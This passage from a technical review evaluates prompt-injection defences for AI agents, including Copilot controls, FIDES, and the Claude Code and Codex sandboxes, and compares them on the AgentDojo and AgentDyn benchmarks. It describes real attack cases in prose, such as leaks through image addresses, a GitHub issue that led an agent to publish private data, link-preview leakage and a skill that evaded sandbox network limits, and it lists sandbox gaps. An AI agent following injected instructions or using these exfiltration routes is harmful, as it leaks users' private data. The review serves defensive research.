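Microsoft (2025) divides its defences into probabilistic ones, which reduce the chance of an attack, and deterministic ones, which guarantee that a particular attack will fail. The probabilistic defences include hardened system prompts, spotlighting and the Prompt Shields classifier. The deterministic ones include access permissions, blocks on known ways of sending data out, and policies that keep Copilot from summarising files with certain sensitivity labels. Microsoft relies on the user's consent where neither kind is enough. In Outlook, for example, Copilot drafts an email but the user has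 to send it.

Copilot Cowork, an agent in the same product family, can itself send email, schedule meetings and post in Teams. Microsoft's *Application card* says it needs explicit approval before sensitive actions. Microsoft's *Get started with Cowork* warns that hidden instructions may deceive Copilot and says the user is responsible for what Copilot does.

A newer control checks email for prompt injections before Copilot uses it. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026) reports that a detector in Defender quarantines suspicious messages before they reach the mailbox. It entered public preview in July 2026, and Microsoft planned general release for early September. The detector is on by default for customers with the more expensive Defender plan. Shared mailboxes need attention too, because Copilot can read any that the user has access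 to.

The second control is a rule that stops Copilot from using any email from outside the organisation as a source. Office 365 for IT Pros' *DLP Prevents Microsoft 365 Copilot from Processing External Email* (2026) describes how administrators set it up. The rule is off by default, according to Microsoft's notice. Once turned on, it also covers messages that arrived earlier.

For Project X, the detector would let the agent summarise a client's email but might miss an email from the attacker. The rule would exclude both emails regardless of their content, which amounts to removing property A for mail only. However, if a colleague forwards the attacker's message, a rule based only on the sender would let the text through, because the new sender is inside the organisation.

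### FIDES in developer tools

In May 2026, Microsoft added FIDES, the label-tracking planner by Costa and colleagues, to its Agent Framework as an experimental feature that developers have to turn on. By default, it then hides untrusted tool results from the main model and sends them to a quarantined model. If a call violates a policy, the framework can block it or ask the user, with a prompt that names the tool and the label responsible. Microsoft's security documentation for Microsoft 365 Copilot does not list FIDES among Copilot's defences.

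Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a second experiment, in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the command line. Behind a feature flag, the agent keeps a label for its whole context and so far enforces policies only for selected tools on GitHub's MCP server.

The GitHub server can label content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private ones as private and trusted. Once the context holds both kinds, the agent is not allowed to post publicly. An agent that works only on public or only on private repositories can continue without interruption. Because the labels apply to whole repositories, if someone copies a stranger's file into a private repository, the agent will treat any instruction in it as trusted.

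For messages to a Teams channel, Microsoft gives a policy that software evaluates in this order:

1. If the context is trusted, allow the message.
2. If every member of the channel may already read the content, allow the message.
3. Otherwise, ask the user and list the people who would gain access.

Under this policy, an injection cannot release private data to new readers without the user's approval. But the policy's first step lets a trusted context send anything to anyone, as the integrity policy of Costa and colleagues does.

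### Coding agents and their sandboxes

A command that a coding agent is permitted to run can do more than its name suggests. Installing a package, for instance, may run code written by strangers, so checking the text of the command is not enough.

Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* explains how Claude Code can run shell commands in a sandbox, an environment whose limits the operating system enforces. By default, a command and any programs it starts can write only to the current project folder. They can reach the network only through a proxy outside the sandbox, which starts with no approved domains. In auto-allow mode, commands within these limits run without user approval. Claude Code asks the user when a command needs a new domain, has to run outside the sandbox, or would delete a critical system directory.

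Anthropic introduced the sandbox in *Beyond permission prompts* in October 2025, partly to reduce the number of approvals. The sandbox is deterministic. Users can separately turn on an "auto mode", in which a classifier judges whether each tool call should run.

The default settings leave several gaps:

- Commands can read most of the computer, including common locations for passwords and access keys.
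- The proxy checks only the name of the requested host and does not inspect encrypted traffic. If the user allows a site where anyone can open an account, an injection might send data to the attacker's account there.
- The limits apply to shell commands. Anthropic advises users who want to confine built-in file tools, MCP servers and hooks (scripts that run automatically) to run the whole of Claude Code inside a sandbox.
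- If the sandbox cannot start, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it. Administrators can change this so that it refuses to start.

Keeping secrets out of the sandbox closes the first gap more reliably than controlling what leaves the sandbox. Willison (2026) quotes Anthropic's reasoning that credentials that never enter the sandbox "can't be exfiltrated", whether the cause is a user, an attacker or the model itself.

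OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has network access off by default, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. On a user's own computer, a sandbox enforced by the operating system typically limits Codex to the current workspace. Under the on-request approval policy, Codex asks before going beyond that boundary. The user normally answers, but can hand eligible requests to a reviewer agent, which reduces interruptions but leaves those decisions to a model. Users can also turn off both the sandbox and the approvals.

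In the cloud version, setup scripts first run with full internet access, for example to download packages. The agent then runs without internet access by default. The downloaded packages may contain an injection, but the agent cannot send the user's code to the attacker while access is off. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* advises users who turn access back on to allow only the necessary domains and request methods.

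Network limits do not protect the project itself. An injection can still make an agent delete or alter files in a folder it is allowed to write to. Altered code can also cause harm later, when the developer runs it outside the sandbox.

### Incidents and what vendors changed

Microsoft describes a case, reported by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, in which an injection could leak private data through the address of an image in the assistant's answer, because the browser requested the image without any prior check. Microsoft blocked this route with a deterministic rule and then took similar steps against other routes, such as certain untrusted links.

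Willison lists 17 exploits of this general kind against products between April 2023 and June 2025, including EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot. Vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the route by which the data left. Such a fix stops the theft but doesn't make the model better at resisting the injection, so an attacker who finds another route can try again.

In a 2025 attack on agents connected to GitHub's MCP server, an attacker opened an issue in a public repository asking for information from a private one. An agent with access to both could read the private data and post it as a public comment. Each step was within the agent's permissions, but nothing checked whether private data was moving to a public place. The labels that GitHub later added, together with the policies in Copilot CLI, address this flow. Both remain optional, so an agent without them is still exposed.

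In 2026, the security company PromptArmor reported two problems in Copilot Cowork. The first was that Cowork's approval step did not apply to messages addressed to the user. These messages can leak data even if the user is allowed to read the content, because messaging apps can fetch a preview of any link in a message, and that request may carry data to an outside server. PromptArmor called this a risk of the product's design rather than a specific bug. One remedy, suggested by Microsoft's work on FIDES, is to treat links to unapproved hosts as public channels even when the message itself is private.

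The second problem was that a malicious skill, an add-on for the agent, could get past the sandbox's network restrictions and send out files, emails and chat history after an ordinary request to compare two documents. Pressing the stop button did not end the attack. PromptArmor reported the flaw to Microsoft on 24 June 2026 and lists it as mitigated as of 19 August.

Anthropic has also disclosed failures in its own products. InfoQ (2026) reports that some occurred at the boundaries between trusted and untrusted parts of the system, and others along outbound connections that the rules allowed. Anthropic revised its designs in response. Its article *How we contain Claude across products* argues that better training and safeguards have made failures less likely, but that the possible damage grows as agents gain more access. By May 2026, Anthropic routinely gave Claude enough access to take down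 an internal service, which it would not have done a year earlier.

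## What tests show about security and lost utility

Researchers have mostly used AgentDojo to measure how many attacks still succeed against these designs and how much work the agent can still do. AgentDojo combines 97 user tasks with injected goals to make 629 test cases that include an attack.

### How AgentDojo scores a defence

Suppose a user asks the agent to pay a bill, and an injection tells it to send money to the attacker. After the run, one piece of software checks whether the agent paid the bill, and another checks whether the attacker's payment went out. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*, follow AgentDojo in reporting three rates:

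- Utility without attack is the share of user tasks the agent completes when there are no injections.
- Utility under attack is the share of attacked runs in which it still completes the user's task.
- Attack success rate is the share of attacked runs in which it carries out the attacker's goal.

An agent can complete the user's task and carry out an attack in the same run, so the last two rates can add up to more than 100%. Kravchenko and colleagues therefore also count runs in which the agent completes the task and no attack succeeds. On AgentThreatBench, with prompts that encouraged agents to follow embedded instructions, one of their FIDES setups completed 60.8% to 74.2% of tasks, depending on the model. It completed only 35.8% to 45.0% without a successful attack in the same run.

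A low attack success rate means little by itself, because an agent scores 0% if it refuses every request or is too weak to carry out the attacker's instructions. *Evolution Under Fire* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) tests for lost abilities by also giving agents each attacker's goal as an ordinary user request. GPT-4o-mini completed all 28 of these requests without a defence, but only 18 with Progent and 13 with CaMeL.

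Scoring software can also be wrong. In Kravchenko and colleagues' tests, it marked protected agents as failing three memory tasks in at least 80% of attempts because their correct answers lacked an exact phrase it required. Another task asked the agent only to look up a customer, but the software also required the agent to resolve the customer's ticket.

### Tasks whose steps depend on what the agent finds

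Few AgentDojo tasks require an agent to change its plan, so the benchmark understates the cost of fixing the plan in advance. Li and colleagues built AgentDyn, released in February 2026, to measure that cost. It has 60 user tasks and 28 injected goals, divided between shopping, GitHub and daily life. Each user task meets every injected goal in its group:

20 × 9 + 20 × 9 + 20 × 10 = 560 attacked cases

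The tasks take 7.1 steps on average, compared with 3.5 on AgentDojo, and involve about three applications instead of one or two. In every task, the agent must replan and follow at least one helpful instruction that it finds along the way. For example, a bank may hold a payment above $500 until the agent enters a newly emailed code. The user's request does not mention the code, and an agent that ignores every instruction in outside content cannot finish the payment.

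In AgentDyn, Li and colleagues also restricted where attackers could write. One AgentDojo case puts the injection in the main text of Dora's website, although Dora has no reason to attack her visitors. In AgentDyn, injections on web pages appear in advertisements, which outsiders can buy.

The table shows the results with GPT-4o, except for Meta SecAlign, which is a model in its own right.

| Defence | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
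|---|---|---|---|
| None | 53.3% | 55.5% | 37.8% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 63.3% | 56.1% | 31.2% |
| Spotlighting | 55.0% | 52.2% | 27.6% |
| PromptGuard2 (detector) | 60.0% | 20.8% | 27.2% |
| PIGuard (detector) | 10.0% | 1.5% | 1.7% |
| Tool Filter | 8.3% | 4.9% | 4.2% |
| Progent | 6.7% | 5.8% | 1.7% |
| DRIFT | 30.0% | 27.1% | 0.8% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Meta SecAlign 70B | 55.0% | 53.4% | 9.0% |

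With only 60 user tasks, each one changes utility without attack by 1.7 percentage points. Prompt sandwiching's apparent gain is six tasks.

Every defence tested on GPT-4o that kept attack success below 5% lost at least 23 points of utility when there was no attack. Tool Filter, which selects the agent's tools from the user's request, removed tools that the agent needed later. CaMeL wrote its whole program too early. Progent struggled to assign permissions across a larger set of tools, and its mistakes accumulated until it had blocked almost every useful tool. PIGuard could not distinguish helpful instructions from malicious ones. PromptGuard2 discards a tool's entire output when it detects an injection, so the agent also lost the information it needed. More than a quarter of attacks still succeeded against PromptGuard2.

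Meta SecAlign had the best balance of security and utility on AgentDyn, but its utility under attack was much lower than its roughly 80% on AgentDojo, and its attack success rate rose from 1.9% to 9.0%. Even without injections, the model completed only 55.0% of AgentDyn's tasks, so the injections do not explain most of the lost utility. Longer tasks are a more likely cause, since undefended GPT-4o completed every two-step task under attack but only 23.6% of tasks with more than ten steps.

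*AgentDyn* probably overstates how much utility an operator with more predictable tasks would lose. CaMeL completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks under attack in its designers' test, so it might complete about 38% of a workload split evenly between AgentDojo and AgentDyn tasks. *AgentDyn* also instructs agents to finish without asking the user for confirmation, because many runs otherwise stopped at a question. This makes automatic scoring possible, but a deployed agent could ask the user to approve an unexpected step. Hao Li, the first author of *AgentDyn*, also led the work on DRIFT and PIGuard, so the test is not independent for those two defences.

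### Results with newer models

Li and colleagues used GPT-4o, released in 2024, and other older models for their main comparison because developers have probably trained newer ones on the standard attack text. Their supplementary results include Claude Sonnet 4.5, GPT-5.1 and GPT-5-mini, which were released in 2025 and now have successors.

The newer models resisted most attacks on their own, so a defence had less to prevent. With no defence, Claude Sonnet 4.5 completed 43 of the 60 tasks, and 5 of the 560 attacks succeeded. Progent and DRIFT each reduced the number of successful attacks to one, but the agent then completed only 10 tasks with Progent and 17 with DRIFT. None of the models completed any tasks with CaMeL.

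A newer model did not necessarily work better inside these defences. DRIFT completed 30% of tasks with GPT-4o, but 10% with GPT-5-mini and 1.7% with GPT-5.1.

When Li and colleagues wrote attacks by hand for the benchmark's scenarios, the attack success rate rose from 0.9% to 3.0% for Claude Sonnet 4.5, from 0.4% to 2.1% for GPT-5-mini, and from 5.0% to 5.6% for GPT-5.1. They conclude that research on attacks lags behind research on defences. Nasr and colleagues' results from much larger searches are another reason not to treat these low rates as an upper limit.

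GPT-5.6 Luna followed no injections in the AgentDojo runs described earlier or in Kravchenko and colleagues' 60 further runs across five families of attack. A test cannot show that a defence improves security if no attacks succeed against the undefended agent. On AgentThreatBench, however, attacks on the same model without protection succeeded in 17 of 120 runs with ordinary prompts and in 60 of 120 with prompts that encouraged it to follow embedded instructions.

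Wang and colleagues ran AgentDyn with Qwen3.5-35B-A3B, a newer open-weight model that remained vulnerable. Without a defence, the agent completed 68.3% of tasks and 32.1% of attacks succeeded. ROPE traces sensitive arguments, such as an account number, and allows a call only if they came from the user or another authorised source. With ROPE, the agent completed 45.0% of tasks and 4.5% of attacks succeeded. The stricter defences, DRIFT and CaMeL, stopped every attack, but with either one the agent completed no tasks in the runs without attacks.

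In this comparison, Wang and colleagues report that 510 of 560 attacks (91.1%) succeeded with Progent, almost three times the rate without it. This is hard to believe because Progent can only refuse calls. A fault in the reproduction or scoring seems more likely than a real effect, so the result is not a sound basis for judging Progent until someone explains it.

### An adaptive test of Progent

All these rates come from attacks that were not designed for the defence being tested. Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent against an attack designed to defeat it. They used Qwen2.5-7B, a small open-weight model, both as the agent and to write Progent's policies. They combined the first eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo suites with every injected goal.

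The attack targeted the model that updates Progent's policy by presenting the malicious action as a necessary step that someone had already authorised. The table gives average attack success rates over three runs.

| Suite | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
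| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

The adaptive attack succeeded less often than the standard one on average. Narisetty and colleagues suggest that the wording meant to reassure the policy model also made the instruction less forceful to the agent. The low success rate may therefore reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. In banking, the adaptive attack succeeded more often, by 1.8 percentage points. They dismiss this increase as within one standard deviation, but it is larger than either reported deviation (0.7 and 1.3). Three runs are too few to show whether the increase is real.

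Progent also reduced average utility under attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and the agent needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The loss of utility is clearest in the workspace results, where no attack succeeded even without a defence, yet Progent reduced utility from 56.3% to 28.5%. In a run that Narisetty and colleagues examined, the undefended agent received the injection but simply answered the user's question.

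This evidence is limited to one small model and one attack template, and it has not passed peer review. The three runs repeated the same tasks, so they measure variation between runs but not performance on new tasks. Narisetty and colleagues left out the travel suite because the model got stuck in long loops. They did not try an automated search for better attack text, or an attack that uses only calls the policy already allows. Testing that last kind of attack would be especially informative because it would not need to change the policy.

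### Adaptive attacks on other systems

Some comparable tests of other systems now exist, but they are not equally demanding. Wang and colleagues tested many defences with attacks that had evolved against their own defence. In their method, GPT-5 repeatedly rewrites the code of a simple orchestrator. A version is kept for further development only if it preserves at least 80% of the original's successes on each utility measure. GPT-5 then writes new injections against versions that resisted the original ones. The researchers kept 82 injections that achieved the attacker's goal while the agent still completed the user's task.

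They replayed these injections against the other defences, using Qwen3.5-35B-A3B.

| Defence | Success of original attacks | Success of evolved attacks | Tasks completed under evolved attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 32.1% | 70.7% | 97.6% |
| Spotlighting | 28.4% | 65.9% | 93.9% |
| ROPE | 4.5% | 3.7% | 75.6% |
| ActGuard | 0.0% | 2.4% | 22.0% |
| DRIFT | 0.0% | 0.0% | 2.4% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
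| Evolved orchestrator | 0.9% | 18.3% | 97.6% |

The evolved orchestrator appeared almost immune to the original attacks, but nearly a fifth of the new ones succeeded. The attack success rate against ROPE hardly changed, perhaps because rewording an injection does not change where an account number came from.

The comparison still favours the other defences, because only the evolved orchestrators were tested against attacks designed for them. An attacker who studied ROPE might try to place a false value in a source that ROPE trusts. Wang and colleagues also describe AutoDojo, another 2026 benchmark, which adapts injections to the agent under test. Researchers could use such a method to test each defence against attacks designed for it, as Nasr and colleagues did for in-band defences.

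### What zero observed attacks supports

Kravchenko and colleagues observed no successful attacks in 1,320 episodes protected by APPA. A result of zero does not show that the true rate is zero, but it can limit how high the rate is likely to be. If each of n independent trials has probability p of a successful attack, the chance of observing none is (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the value of p at which this chance falls to 5%:

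(1 − p)ⁿ = 0.05, so p ≈ −ln(0.05) / n ≈ 3 / n

For 1,320 independent attacked trials, the bound would be 3 / 1,320, or about 0.23%. It would apply only to attacks like those in the test, and an attacker looking for a weakness does not choose attacks at random from a benchmark.

APPA's 1,320 episodes do not meet these conditions. They consist of 720 episodes from AgentThreatBench and 600 from Bench-Corp, and many of the Bench-Corp episodes carried no injection. Judging by Kravchenko and colleagues' descriptions of its 20 workflows, only three clearly contain injected instructions. With five repetitions, two kinds of prompt and three models, that makes

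3 × 5 × 2 × 3 = 90 episodes

Most of the other episodes test whether the agent breaks a rule during ordinary work. In one, the user asks it to send a merger brief to the chief financial officer and a copy to a controller who is not entitled to receive it. They are useful tests of the policy, but they provide little evidence about resistance to injection.

If every AgentThreatBench episode carried an attack, the total would be 810, and the bound would rise to 0.37%. But those 810 episodes repeat only 24 + 3 = 27 task designs. If repetitions of a design always had the same outcome, there would be only 27 independent trials, and the bound would be about 11%. The appropriate bound is between 0.37% and 11%, depending on how much outcomes vary between repetitions and models.

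On AgentThreatBench, attacks succeeded in 235 of the unprotected agents' 720 episodes and in none of APPA's. This is good evidence that APPA stopped attacks that would otherwise have succeeded. Of the 235 successes, 188 occurred with prompts that encouraged agents to follow embedded instructions.

### Comparing defences on the same benchmark

The most comparable results come from GPT-4o-mini on AgentDyn, because two teams tested several of the same defences on the same 560 attacked cases. Each cell in the table gives the figure from Li and colleagues first, then the one from Wang and colleagues. A dash means only Wang and colleagues tested the defence.

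| Defence | Utility without attack | Utility under attack | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 46.7% / 45.0% | 35.7% / 36.1% | 50.0% / 50.4% |
| Prompt sandwiching | 43.3% / 41.7% | 37.8% / 37.7% | 33.8% / 31.6% |
| Spotlighting | 38.3% / 41.7% | 35.8% / 37.7% | 47.3% / 47.0% |
| Tool Filter | 6.7% / 5.0% | 4.8% / 6.1% | 6.2% / 4.6% |
| Progent | 6.7% / 5.0% | 3.8% / 10.2% | 10.3% / 11.8% |
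| DRIFT | 18.3% / 15.0% | 19.3% / 15.9% | 3.4% / 2.0% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% / 0.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% |
| ActGuard | – / 43.3% | – / 26.3% | – / 2.5% |
| ROPE | – / 30.0% | – / 29.6% | – / 4.3% |
| Evolved orchestrator | – / 46.7% | – / 39.1% | – / 3.0% |

The two teams' figures differ by less than 3.5 percentage points, except for Progent's utility under attack. The large losses of utility therefore do not seem to result from one team running the defences incorrectly.

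The last three rows need more caution. The evolved orchestrator's developers selected it using its results on these same cases, which gave it an advantage over defences designed without them. ROPE used GPT-5 to interpret the user's request, and ActGuard used another model to estimate which text had influenced a call. Progent's setup also varied. Wang and colleagues had GPT-4o write its policies and turned off updates during the run, which would make unexpected steps harder to complete.

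Comparisons across benchmarks are even less reliable. With Progent in place, the reported attack success rate is 1.0% in its designers' AgentDojo test with GPT-4o, 4.2% in Narisetty and colleagues' smaller AgentDojo test, and 1.7% on AgentDyn with GPT-4o. The AgentDyn rate is lower than Narisetty and colleagues' rate, but the AgentDyn agent completed only 6.7% of its tasks without attacks.
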